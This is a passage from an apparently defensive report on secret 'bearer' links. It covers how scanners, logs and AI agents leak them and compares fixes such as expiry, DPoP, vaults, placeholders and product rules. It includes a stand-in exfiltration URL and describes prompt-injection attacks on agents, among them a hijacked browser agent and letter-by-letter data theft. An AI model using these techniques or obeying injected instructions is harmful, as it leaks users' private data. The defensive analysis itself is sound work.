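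Tennison recommends answering requests for an expired link with one of two standard errors. The stricter one, "410 Gone", requires the site to keep a record of its old tokens. That record also keeps the site from giving the same token to another customer, as the loan site whose link opened two applicants' records had apparently done.

### Single use and the confirming click

A single-use link stops working after its first use, so any remaining copies are harmless. But if a scanner opens it before the patient does, the link won't work for the patient.

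To get around this, Pulse Security suggests that the site either allow a few uses, perhaps three, or show a "view this item" button and count a use only when somebody presses it. Both options weaken the protection. If the mail filter takes one of three uses and the patient takes another, a stranger can use the third. With a button, the scanner no longer uses up the link, so the copy in the public feed works until somebody presses the button or the link expires. This matters most for a password reset that an attacker requested, because the account's owner has no reason to press the button. A site that adds a button to its reset links should also make them expire quickly.

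A single-use link also works only for whoever opens it first. If that is a stranger, the patient gets an error message, which is at least a sign that something went wrong. The site could explain this instead of just reporting an invalid link. *OAuth 2.0 Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP)* (Fett, Campbell and colleagues, 2023), an internet standard for protecting tokens, warns that a large service may run many copies of its server, and some may briefly accept a used code because the record of its use has not reached them yet.

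A confirming click also helps prevent accidental actions. Browsers normally fetch a page with a GET request and submit a form with a POST request. Tennison advises that a GET request to a capability URL should never delete anything or have similar side effects. Clicking an emailed link can only send a GET request, so a link for cancelling an appointment should open a page with a "Cancel appointment" button that sends the POST request. A mail filter that opens the link will usually load the page without pressing the button.

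The button adds one click for the user. It does not prevent a stranger from reading the page, and some programs will press it. Visitors to Mustafa and colleagues' decoy pages used a form, button or menu in 7% of visits.

### A second check, or a login

A site can require proof that the visitor is the intended recipient. In a design that Pulse Security saw in a medical application, the link opens a page with no private data, and the site emails the patient a short-lived code, which the patient enters to see the document. Someone who finds the link in a public feed, a server log or a Slack channel can't get past the first page.

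A six-digit code has only about 20 bits of entropy, not many more than a birth date, which some lenders ask for, so its protection comes from the limit on guesses. If the site cancels the code after five wrong answers, a stranger has a 1 in 200,000 chance of guessing it. The site also has to limit requests for new codes, or the stranger can keep starting again. A birth date is weaker than a fresh random code even with a strict limit on guesses, because it never changes and other people may know it.

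The server must also hold back all private data until the visitor passes the check. Danish and colleagues found five services that revealed part of the customer's information before the check. Three of the services that sent browsers more data than they displayed used GraphQL, which lets a page request only the fields it needs, but their pages requested every field.

Pulse Security considers the emailed code a poor experience for users, who have to wait for a second message just after opening the first. As a compromise, it suggests letting the link work without a code for about ten days, then requiring one. This would annoy fewer of the clinic's patients, but a mail filter is most likely to publish the link during those ten days. For medical records, Pulse Security thinks an unprotected link may not be acceptable, even briefly.

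An emailed code does not stop anyone who can read the mailbox, including a hijacked agent like the one in Brave's Comet demonstration. If the clinic texted the code instead, an agent with access only to the patient's email would have to ask the patient for it, and the patient could refuse. But an agent working on its own overnight would be unable to continue until the patient replied.

Recipients who already have an account can log in instead. This lets the site remove one person's access without affecting anyone else's. If the site asks new customers to register, it must check that they control the email address that received the link. Otherwise, a stranger with the link could register first. Logging in takes more effort than entering a code, and people who forget their passwords will need a reset link, which is another bearer link. The patient also can no longer simply forward the invoice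 to a partner.

For some links, neither method is possible. When a supplier shares a contract with "anyone with the link", Google does not know who should receive it, so it has no address to send a code to. Pulse Security expects file-sharing services that work this way to remain vulnerable. The supplier can restrict the file to named accounts, but must then find out which colleagues need it.

### Cancelling links and reading the logs

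An owner who discovers a leak needs a way to cancel the link. If each recipient has a separate link, the owner can cancel the leaked one without cutting off everyone else. Sites can also limit the damage from a leak by using separate links for different powers. The scheduling site Doodle, one of Tennison's examples, gives the organiser of a poll one link for participants and another for changing or deleting the poll. If the visa site in the LEAKYLINKS study had used a read-only link for showing the visa, a stranger could still have copied the passport number but could not have edited the application.

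Cancelling a leaked link depends on somebody noticing the leak. Server logs can help when the pattern is obvious. If the clinic emailed a link to one patient and it was opened from 30 IP addresses within an hour, the link has probably leaked. One extra visit is much harder to interpret, since it could come from the patient's phone, the employer's mail filter or a thief.

Agents will make these logs harder to interpret. An agent that runs in the cloud opens the invoice from a data centre, much as an unwanted scanner would, so a clinic that blocks data centres may also block agents that its patients chose to use. Logs can also leak links, which the clinic can avoid by recording an internal number for each link instead of its token.

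### Where to put the secret

The token should be long and random, wherever it appears in the address. Danish and colleagues recommend at least 64 bits from a cryptographically secure random number generator, but Tennison's 120 bits is better for a large service. The few extra characters don't inconvenience the user, except perhaps in a text message.

Programs can keep a secret out of the address by sending it in a request header. OWASP's *9.3 Sensitive data does not get sent in the URL*, part of a widely used set of security requirements, allows sensitive data only in a request's headers or body. A header does not protect the secret if the program's first request is unencrypted. Many sites redirect such requests to the encrypted version, but IETF's *Protecting Credentials with HTTP APIs* (2026), a draft guide for developers, points out that the secret has already crossed the network unencrypted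 by then.

An emailed link can't send its token in a header, but the site can redirect the browser to an address without the token, as in login by email. This hides the token from scripts on the final page, but not from the mailbox or the mail filter. It will also confuse patients who copy the new address for a partner, because it won't work for the partner.

Tennison describes another method, in which a script on the page replaces the address in the address bar. This hides the token from people looking at the screen, but the user can no longer bookmark the working link.

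**Hostnames.** A secret should never go in the hostname, as the Muse chats showed. There can be good reasons to give each user's content its own hostname, however. Tennison explains that some sites do this so that content from one user does not get the privileges that browsers give to pages on the main site. The main site's login cookies would undermine this separation, so the site needs another way to control access, and a token in the address is a convenient one. It can go in the path:

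`https://chat-48213.usercontent.example/b7Qm4xT9vLr2KfZ8`

Passive DNS would reveal that chat 48213 exists, but not how to open it.

A site can put the token in the link's fragment, the part after the #, which keeps it out of ordinary request logs and the Referer header. The site then needs a script to read the token, and it can no longer use the fragment to jump to part of a page. Mail filters still receive the complete link, so using a fragment does little to prevent the leaks that have turned up in public feeds.

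### Referer policies and search engines

By default, modern browsers leave the path and query out of the `Referer` header they send to other sites. For pages with a token in the address, developers can set the `no-referrer` policy, which removes the header entirely. Users notice no difference, but the sites they visit next lose some information about where their visitors came from.

Referer leaks did damage before the default changed, and sometimes afterwards. Zagi, Moti and Acar (2025) report in *Referrer Policy* that a Trainline website sent outside companies tokens that opened customers' bookings. In 2021, the tutoring site UPchieve turned out to have a similar flaw that exposed password-reset tokens.

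But W3C's *Referrer Policy*, the standard that defines these settings, acknowledges that controlling the header does not stop every leak of a capability URL. Zagi and colleagues visited more than 100,000 pages on 27,750 websites, using connections in the United States, Singapore and the Netherlands. On 77.20% of the sites, page addresses or parts of them reached other companies despite a policy that should have withheld them. Advertising and analytics scripts, including those of Google Analytics, Facebook and TikTok, were often responsible. They read the address from the page and sent it separately, without altering the Referer header.

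The 77.20% figure suggests that an ordinary analytics script on the clinic's invoice page would send the invoice link to the script's owner. The figure is not a count of leaked tokens, since most of these addresses probably contained no secret. The clinic can prevent such a leak by keeping other companies' scripts off such pages, or by redirecting to an address without the secret before any of those scripts load, though it would lose some visitor statistics.

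Instructions to search engines are weaker still. A `noindex` header does not work if the site also blocks the page in robots.txt, as Anthropic did with shared Claude chats. Mozilla's web security guidelines recommend a Referer policy for all websites but treat robots.txt as optional. Anyone can read that file, so a shop that listed `/new-prices` there would reveal the page it wanted to hide. Neither `noindex` nor robots.txt keeps a link out of a scanning service's feed.

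### Tokens that need a key

All the tokens so far work for anyone who has a copy. The DPoP standard, also known as RFC 9449, changes this for applications that use OAuth. It relies on a pair of keys: a private key that creates digital signatures, and a public key that anyone can use to check them. Suppose the clinic's billing company offered a phone app:

1. The app creates a pair of keys and keeps the private key on the phone.
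2. It asks the server for an access token and signs the request. The server ties the new token to the app's public key.
3. For every later request, the app signs a new proof. This contains the address and type of the request, the time, a unique identifier and a fingerprint of the token.
4. The server checks that the signature matches the token's key and that the proof fits the request. If anything is wrong, it refuses.

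A stranger who finds the token in a log can't use it alone, because they can't sign the proof that must go with it. Stealing a proof too helps only a little, because each proof works for only one address and, in a well-run system, expires within seconds or minutes. The server can also reject a proof whose identifier it has already seen.

Fett and colleagues describe two limits. Hostile code running inside the app can make the app sign any request, even if the code can't copy the private key. An insider can also prepare proofs with future dates. In their example, a bank employee creates proofs on a work computer and uses them later on another machine to get around the bank's audit controls. The server can prevent this by requiring each proof to include a recent, unpredictable value that the server chose.

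This design works much better for software than for links in emails. When the clinic sends an invoice, it doesn't know which device the patient will use, so it has no key to tie the link to. It could tie the link to the first browser that opens it, but that browser may belong to a scanning service. The patient also couldn't open the invoice on a second device or forward it.

An agent, on the other hand, is software and can have its own key. If the patient allowed an agent to read invoices through the billing company's programming interface, the program around the model could hold the key and sign the requests. The model might then repeat the token in a summary, or a tool might write it to a log, but colleagues who saw it could not use it without the key. This works only if the private key never enters the model's context, because the model could repeat the key too.

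The server can't use the key to check what the patient wanted. If an attacker uses an email to trick the agent into fetching every invoice, the program will sign those requests just as it signs legitimate ones. The attacker may then obtain the invoices' contents, even though the token won't work outside the agent's software. The patient therefore still needs to give the agent narrow permissions, such as reading this month's invoices, and a separate token that the patient can cancel.

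### What scanning services could hide

Scanning services could make scans private by default. A badly configured mail filter would then no longer leak an employer's secret links through the public feed. Mustafa and colleagues call this the radical approach and expect it to affect the services' business, which depends partly on sharing results. Security teams would also lose a free source of information about new phishing sites.

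Their narrower proposal is to run a check like LEAKYLINKS on each scan and make the result private if the page shows sensitive personal information. They estimate that hiding every such page in the six feeds would remove about 0.24% of the published links.

That figure assumes perfect detection, but LEAKYLINKS would miss about 22% of the sensitive links, according to the team's error estimates. The figure is also low because most entries in the feeds are base addresses, but even among the full links that remained after filtering, the loss would be only 1.6%.

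A bigger concern for security teams is that the check could hide phishing pages. Some of these pages have the victim's email address already filled in, and a vision model could mistake them for private account pages. Criminals might also add invented personal details to keep their pages out of the feeds. The study does not settle this, because the researchers removed known malicious links before running the model. A service could let vetted researchers see the hidden results, but urlscan.io's unlisted scans work in much the same way, and strangers opened Vin01's decoys there.

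Computing power should not be a serious obstacle, since LEAKYLINKS needed so little. But the checks would have to finish before a link is published, because an attacker can copy it within seconds.

urlscan.io already uses simpler methods. It told the researchers that it blocks certain domains, lets users report leaks and refuses to scan addresses with words such as "unsubscribe" in the path. It acknowledged that these measures did not prevent every leak and said it planned to detect sensitive links automatically. The researchers' results support that admission: 664 of the 1,861 sensitive pages from urlscan.io dealt with mailing-list preferences and subscriptions, the kind of page that the word filter should often catch.

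Cloudflare's feed changed much more. Its share of full links fell from about 20.1% in the pilot study to 1.7% in the main study. At the pilot's rate, the feed would have contained about 89,000 full links during the three weeks of the main study instead of 7,474. If 3% of those had been sensitive, as in the main study, the feed would have exposed around 2,700 private pages instead of 224.

Mustafa and colleagues believe their report to Cloudflare led to the drop, but they infer this from the timing. Cloudflare's customers may have changed what they submitted, or somebody may have started scanning large numbers of base addresses, which would lower the share of full links even if their number stayed the same. A statement from Cloudflare or a week-by-week count would help show what caused the drop. Removing paths and queries would not protect a secret in the hostname, because a feed of base addresses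 still lists every hostname.

### Remedies and leak routes

| Remedy | Leak routes it addresses | What it leaves open | Measured effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short lifetime | Old mailboxes, logs and archives | Leaks before expiry, saved screenshots | None |
| Single use | Copies found after the first use | Whoever opens the link first | Indirect: most password-sharing links in public databases were already used up |
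| Confirming click | Accidental actions by scanners and agents | Reading the page | Indirect: 7% of decoy visits used a form, button or menu |
| Random code with few tries, or a login | Any route that exposes only the link | Access to the mailbox or account | None |
| Separate links that the owner can cancel | Further use after a known leak | Leaks that nobody notices | None |
| Token in the path, not the hostname | Passive DNS | Mail filters, scripts, agents | None |
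| Strict Referer policy | The Referer header | Scripts on the page | Its limits: page addresses still got out on 77.20% of sites |
| `noindex` | Search results | Every other route | None |
| Token tied to a key (DPoP) | Tokens copied from logs, chats or an agent's context | A hijacked app or agent | None |
| Hiding sensitive scans | Public feeds | Pages the check misses | Estimate only: 0.24% fewer published links |
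| Publishing fewer full addresses | Public feeds | Secrets in hostnames | Yes, at Cloudflare: from 20.1% to 1.7%, cause inferred |

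## Safer handling: what agent developers and users can change

Even if the dental clinic never improves its links, the developer of the patient's agent can limit which addresses the agent opens, hide tokens from the model and check what the agent publishes. The patient can change some settings too. Developers built many of these protections to stop prompt injection, so the protections are often less effective when an agent repeats a private link by mistake.

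### OpenAI's public-index rule

In January 2026, OpenAI explained when ChatGPT and its agents may load an address without asking the user. The company uses a crawler that records the addresses of public web pages and has no access to users' conversations or accounts. Before an agent loads a page or image automatically, the software checks whether the crawler has recorded that exact address.

If it has, the agent loads the address. If it hasn't, the software either tells the agent to try another website or warns the user that the address may contain information from the conversation. The user can still choose to open it.

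The address from the earlier attack example, `https://stranger.example/log?note=[text from the mailbox]`, would fail this check. The crawler could not have recorded it in advance, because part of it comes from the patient's private mail.

Johann Rehberger, who reported this kind of leak to OpenAI in early 2023, discusses the accompanying paper in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. OpenAI added a first check in December 2023, but he found ways around it and places where it was missing, such as the macOS and iOS apps. He calls the new rule a significant improvement but warns that OpenAI's own developers may not always apply it.

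The paper also acknowledges that a letter-by-letter attack can still work if the crawler has recorded the attacker's page for each letter and digit. Rehberger suggests that the agent never open the same address twice in a session. This would disrupt the simplest version of the attack, because a 16-character token usually repeats a character. But an attacker could publish a separate page for each character in each position. For the clinic's token, that would take 16 × 62 = 992 pages, and the agent would open only 16 of them.

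Neither OpenAI's post nor Rehberger's article reports how many attacks the rule stops or how often it delays a harmless page.

### What the rule means for bearer links

OpenAI designed the rule for addresses that an attacker has filled with stolen data. The effects on genuine bearer links described here are inferences from how the rule works.

The crawler normally won't know the clinic's invoice link, so the agent can't load it automatically. Trying another source won't help because no other website has the invoice, so the patient will probably see a warning. OpenAI has a stricter rule for email. *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* reports that after an attack that stole data one letter at a time, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from opening links from emails unless they appear in a public index or meet another condition.

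The warning gives the patient a chance to stop the agent from using up a password-reset link, but it will also appear for many harmless links. If the patient's agent tried to open 20 private links a month, and an attacker's address turned up once in ten years, the patient would see 2,400 warnings about harmless links for each warning about the attacker's. OpenAI worries that frequent warnings train people to click through them, and gives this as a reason not to rely on a strict list of trusted sites.

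An agent may open an already leaked bearer link without warning the user. If a scanning service published the clinic's link and OpenAI's crawler recorded it in the index, the agent could load the invoice automatically. The extra visit does little harm unless opening the link triggers an action, but the patient would not learn that the invoice had become public. A developer could use the index to detect such leaks and alert the patient when a link from a personal email appears in it.

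OpenAI's rule also doesn't keep the link secret. The link is already in the agent's context when the software checks it, and may be in the logs. The agent can still write it into a Slack summary, and Slack's servers can then open it to make a preview, because the rule controls only OpenAI's own software.

### Lockdown Mode

ChatGPT users can turn on Lockdown Mode, which limits browsing to cached pages so that it sends no live requests outside OpenAI's controlled network, according to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*. An attacker's website then receives nothing, even if the agent obeys a hostile instruction to visit it. But the agent also can't open the clinic's invoice unless OpenAI has a cached copy.

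Turning on Lockdown Mode removes many ChatGPT features. According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the setting disables agent mode and deep research, stops ChatGPT from downloading files for analysis, and may hide images in its answers. On personal accounts, it also blocks live access to connected services where that access would conflict with its protections. In larger organisations, administrators choose which apps remain available.

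Lockdown Mode does not change ChatGPT's memory or the user's ability to share a conversation, so a patient who has pasted the invoice link into a chat can still share that chat. It also does not affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. OpenAI recommends the mode for people and organisations that handle sensitive data, but warns that some risk remains, for example through apps an administrator has enabled.

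### Other companies' rules

Anthropic's web fetch tool opens only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation. Its current documentation, *網頁擷取工具* (in Chinese), adds a second rule that matters more for bearer links. The tool won't open addresses that seem to contain a credential, such as an API key or a password, unless the credential appears in the developer's instructions or the text of a user's message, not just in a tool's result.

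If a mailbox tool returns the clinic's link, Claude may therefore be unable to open it. This depends on whether Anthropic's software recognises `key=b7Qm4xT9vLr2KfZ8` as a credential. A token in the path, with no label such as `key`, might be harder to recognise. If Claude can't open the link, the patient can paste it into the chat, but this creates another copy of it.

The tool also rejects addresses longer than 250 characters. This limits how much stolen data one address can carry, but it would block some long pre-signed file links.

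Willison (2026) reports that Claude's chat app no longer follows links inside pages it has fetched. According to the developer documentation, the fetch tool can still follow them by default, but developers can turn this off with the `url_sources` setting. In an earlier version of the documentation, Anthropic advised developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with non-sensitive data.

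Google also uses an index, but for speed. Google Cloud's *URL context* describes a tool that lets Gemini models read pages at addresses developers supply. The tool first looks for the page in Google's web index and, if it isn't there, fetches it live after a content moderation check on the address. Gemini's tool therefore visits an unknown address automatically, whereas ChatGPT shows a warning. The tool does not support Google Docs, so it could not read the supplier's contract if that were a Google Doc.

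OpenClaw, the agent that people often use through messaging apps, can fall back on an outside service, Firecrawl, when its fetch tool fails to extract a page's text. If this happened with the invoice, Firecrawl would receive the whole link. A user who handles private links can avoid this by leaving Firecrawl disabled.

The last column of this table is inferred from the documented rules:

| Product | Rule for opening an address | The clinic's link, found in an email |
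|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT | Automatic if a public crawler has recorded it | Probably a warning |
| ChatGPT in Lockdown Mode | Cached pages only | Does not open |
| Claude's web fetch tool | Must already be in the conversation and not seem to contain a credential | May be refused |
| Gemini's URL context tool | Index first, then a live visit | Opens if it passes the moderation check |
| OpenClaw | Fetches the page, with Firecrawl as a possible fallback | Opens, and may go to Firecrawl |

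### Keeping credentials in a vault

These rules all apply after the model has read the link. A vault is a program that keeps the secret away from the model. The model receives only a name for the secret, such as "GitHub connection". When the agent sends a request to GitHub, trusted software outside the model adds the key.

Kenney and colleagues tested such a vault on September 27, 2026. They work for Corvic AI, which makes it. They ran fixed test code in the environment where the company's agents execute programs, and decided before each test what a secure result would be. One experiment had a connection to GitHub and the other to FRED, a service for economic data. The tests looked for leaks in several places:

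- **The environment.** The code searched its environment variables and 12 common locations for credential files, and found no key.
- **Other websites.** It called three "echo" services, which send back whatever request they receive. None of the replies contained the key.
- **Other companies' services.** It called OpenAI's interface while connected to GitHub. OpenAI answered that the request had no credentials, so the vault had not sent the GitHub key there.
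- **Cloud accounts.** It tried two addresses from which programs on cloud servers can often obtain credentials. Neither responded.

The code also had to make a normal request to GitHub, which succeeded even though the code never had the key. Without that check, a system with no internet connection could have passed most of the others. All 16 checks gave the expected result.

The connection to FRED was secure but failed because FRED requires its key in the query part of the address, and the vault was set to send it in a header. A correct setting might have fixed this. But a website that emails a bearer link always expects the token in the address, so a vault for links would have to put it there, and the complete address could then appear in redirects, error messages and logs. The researchers didn't test redirects or browser tools.

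They also didn't test whether a hostile email could make an agent misuse a connection. A vault can't prevent this by itself, because an agent that never sees the GitHub key can still ask the vault to delete a project. Kenney and colleagues scored each threat from 1 to 25 before and after adding the vault. In their judgement, the risk from pasting a secret into a chat falls from 25 to 4, but the risk from prompt injection falls only from 25 to 12, and the risk from connections with too many permissions only from 20 to 15.

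### Placeholders for links

A developer could apply the same idea to bearer links. The following design is an illustration, not a tested product. Suppose the clinic's email contains this sentence:

`Your invoice is ready: https://northgate-dental.billing.example/invoices/2291?key=b7Qm4xT9vLr2KfZ8`

The mail tool stores the address and gives the model this version:

`Your invoice is ready: [link-1, northgate-dental.billing.example]`

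1. The model asks the fetch tool to open `link-1`.
2. The fetch tool looks up the real address and requests the page.
3. Before returning the page to the model, the tool replaces every address in it with another placeholder. Pages often contain their own address, for example behind a "share" button.
4. The model reports that the patient owes $85 and cites `link-1`.
5. In the patient's private chat, the software turns the placeholder into a clickable link. In Slack, it writes "email from Northgate Dental, Tuesday".

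The model can now summarise the invoice without being able to repeat the token. It still sees the hostname, which helps it judge whether the message is genuine. If it posts the placeholder in the wrong place, nobody there can use it.

This could even improve the agent's work, since removing irrelevant details helped in the shopping tests by Roh and colleagues. But it could make some tasks harder, such as comparing two versions of a web address, because the agent needs to see both.

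Secret links are harder to remove from screenshots than from text. A screenshot of the browser may expose the token to the agent in the address bar or in a QR code, and a program that replaces text will miss both. The developer can crop out the address bar, but would need image recognition to find a link shown on the page.

The method also fails when somebody needs the real link. Once the patient clicks it, the patient's own browser has a copy. The supplier's contract is harder to handle because the whole team needs to open it. The software would have to put the real link into the Slack message, so it would first have to know that the team is allowed to open the contract but not the invoice. Asking the patient is probably the simplest way to find out.

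### Cleaning logs and answers

Developers also have to keep links out of their own logs. Kenney and colleagues recommend removing signed links and secrets in queries but keeping an identifier so engineers can trace faults. A log entry could record that the agent opened `link-1` at the clinic's hostname and received the page.

Skills sometimes print secrets, so the developer should also remove secrets from a tool's output before the model reads it. If the developer removes them only from the final answer, the secrets will already be in the conversation history and the provider's copy.

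Without placeholders, the software must work out which addresses are secret. It can remove everything after the question mark, but this breaks many ordinary links and misses tokens in the path. It can also look for random-looking strings, but a loose test would cause many false alarms. A filter that removed every link flagged by the LEAKYLINKS token check would have removed about 50 harmless links for each sensitive one. The links in that study came from scanning feeds, so the ratio for an agent's answers could be quite different.

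Before an agent posts a summary, the software could also check its links against a public index, keep those that a crawler has recorded, and replace the others with descriptions. This would remove the invoice link and usually keep citations to news articles. The team would also lose the contract link unless the patient approved it, and a private link that had already leaked into the index would still be posted. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks* lists removing suspicious addresses among Gemini's defences, but that is meant to stop an attacker's links, and the clinic's genuine link may not look suspicious.

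Deleting logs and conversations early gives the links in them less time to leak. If the chance of a leak grows steadily with time, keeping a working link in a log for 30 days instead of a year cuts that chance by a factor of 12. The shorter period makes no difference for a reset link that expires after an hour.

A data retention agreement with the model provider covers only the provider's copies of a link. Anthropic offers developers "zero data retention" for its basic fetch tool, but warns that the website may keep anything in the address it receives. The newer version of the tool lets Claude write code to filter a page before the text enters its context. That could keep out unneeded links, but the filtering isn't eligible for zero data retention, so a developer may have to choose between the two.

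Once a link has leaked, its owner has to cancel the secret, because deleting the known copies isn't enough. Chen and colleagues found that secrets removed from 107 original code repositories remained in more than 50 independent copies of those repositories.

### Previews and browser profiles

Apps that post to Slack can turn off previews for a message by setting both `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false (Willison, 2024). Colleagues lose the title and picture but can still open the link. Turning previews off also makes theft harder. PromptArmor explains that without them, a user would typically have to click an attacker's link before any data escaped.

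Some agents preview links automatically, which brings untrusted text from the linked page into the agent's context before the user has asked to open anything. The test agent in *Silent Egress* (2026) did this, and the researchers could place hostile instructions in a page's title, description or comments. A developer can avoid this by having the agent open a link only when the task requires it.

Users can also give an agent its own browser profile, with separate cookies, saved passwords, history and extensions. In Brave's Comet demonstration, the hijacked agent could read the login code because the user was already logged in to Gmail. An agent in a fresh profile would have found Gmail's login page.

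A separate profile protects bearer links much less, since they work in any browser. It can help after an agent opens a one-time login link, because deleting the profile removes the cookie that keeps the agent logged in. But the patient must log in again, inside the new profile, to every account the agent needs, and each login restores some of the access the profile was meant to keep from the agent.

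### Approval before publishing

Kenney and colleagues recommend requiring a person's approval before an agent publishes anything outside the organisation. In Cyberhaven's test, agents usually published confidential material without asking, so the developer should build the approval step into the publishing tool instead of relying on the model to ask.

The approval screen also has to show what the user needs to know to decide, including what any hidden address opens. For example, it might show that 14 people will see the message and that one of its links opens a dental invoice without a login. The software can check whether a link works without a login by opening it in a browser with no cookies, as LEAKYLINKS did, but it should not do this with links that may work only once.

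Whether an action needs approval should depend on who can see the result. OpenAI advises organisations using Lockdown Mode not to enable actions that change something in an app unless administrators can confirm that no malicious person will see the result. Saving a draft in the patient's own folder is less risky than posting in a channel with unknown members. Creating a public code repository, as agents may have done in PixelLeak, should require approval even if the only planned upload is a screenshot.

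Frequent approval requests cause the same problem as frequent link warnings. If the patient approves a summary every morning, one that contains a reset link may get no more attention than the others. The tool could automatically post summaries that contain no links and ask for approval only for the rest.

### Telling the model to keep secrets

A developer can also instruct the model not to reveal private links. This is easy, but the results are unreliable. *The Framing Gap* (2026) tested whether hostile text could make agents send out a confidential value from their context. A policy that forbade disclosure "in any form" reduced the leak rate from 31.9% to zero. When the policy named specific behaviours without that general phrase, the rate was 48.8%. In the shopping tests by Roh and colleagues, an instruction to leave out irrelevant information increased oversharing.

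A separate detector built only to recognise hostile instructions did better, catching every variant of the attack with no false alarms. The results are encouraging, but they come from the study's own set of attacks. The detector also would not help with an ordinary email from the clinic, which contains no hostile instructions.

The same study found no leaks in 48 valid trials with the ChatGPT product, although the model leaked in up to 100% of trials through OpenAI's programming interface. With 48 trials, the product's true leak rate could still be as high as about 7%. The protections around the model, possibly including the public-index rule, could explain the difference, but the researchers could not inspect the product to check.

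### Tracking where private data may go

Software can also track who is allowed to see each piece of information, a method called information-flow tracking. Kenney and colleagues cite CaMeL, a system that works out the steps of a task from the user's own request and checks each tool call against a policy. With CaMeL, text in an email can supply data for the task but cannot add a step such as "send this to a stranger".

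For the dental patient's summary, a system of this kind could work as follows:

1. The patient asks for a summary of unread mail in the team's Slack channel. The software fixes the steps before the model reads any messages: read the mail, summarise it and post the result.
2. It labels the clinic's email "patient only" and the supplier's email "team".
3. Anything the agent makes from an email inherits its label. If the agent combines both emails, the stricter label applies.
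4. Before posting, the software compares the label with the members of the channel. It stops the invoice and allows the contract.

Step 3 can easily block too much. One sentence about the invoice would make the whole summary "patient only", even though most of it is harmless. The agent could summarise each message separately, so that the software withholds only the private part, but then it could not combine information from several messages.

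Someone also has to provide the labels. The clinic's email doesn't state who may read it, and a wrong label on the contract would keep it from the team. Labelling all mail "patient only" is safer, but the patient would have to approve every exception.

Unlike filters that search for tokens, labels can protect a secret that the software doesn't recognise. A screenshot of the invoice would be labelled "patient only" even if no program could read the address in it, so the agent could not upload it to a public repository without permission. This works only if every tool preserves the label. If one tool saves the screenshot as an ordinary file and another uploads it, the second tool has no label showing that the image is private.
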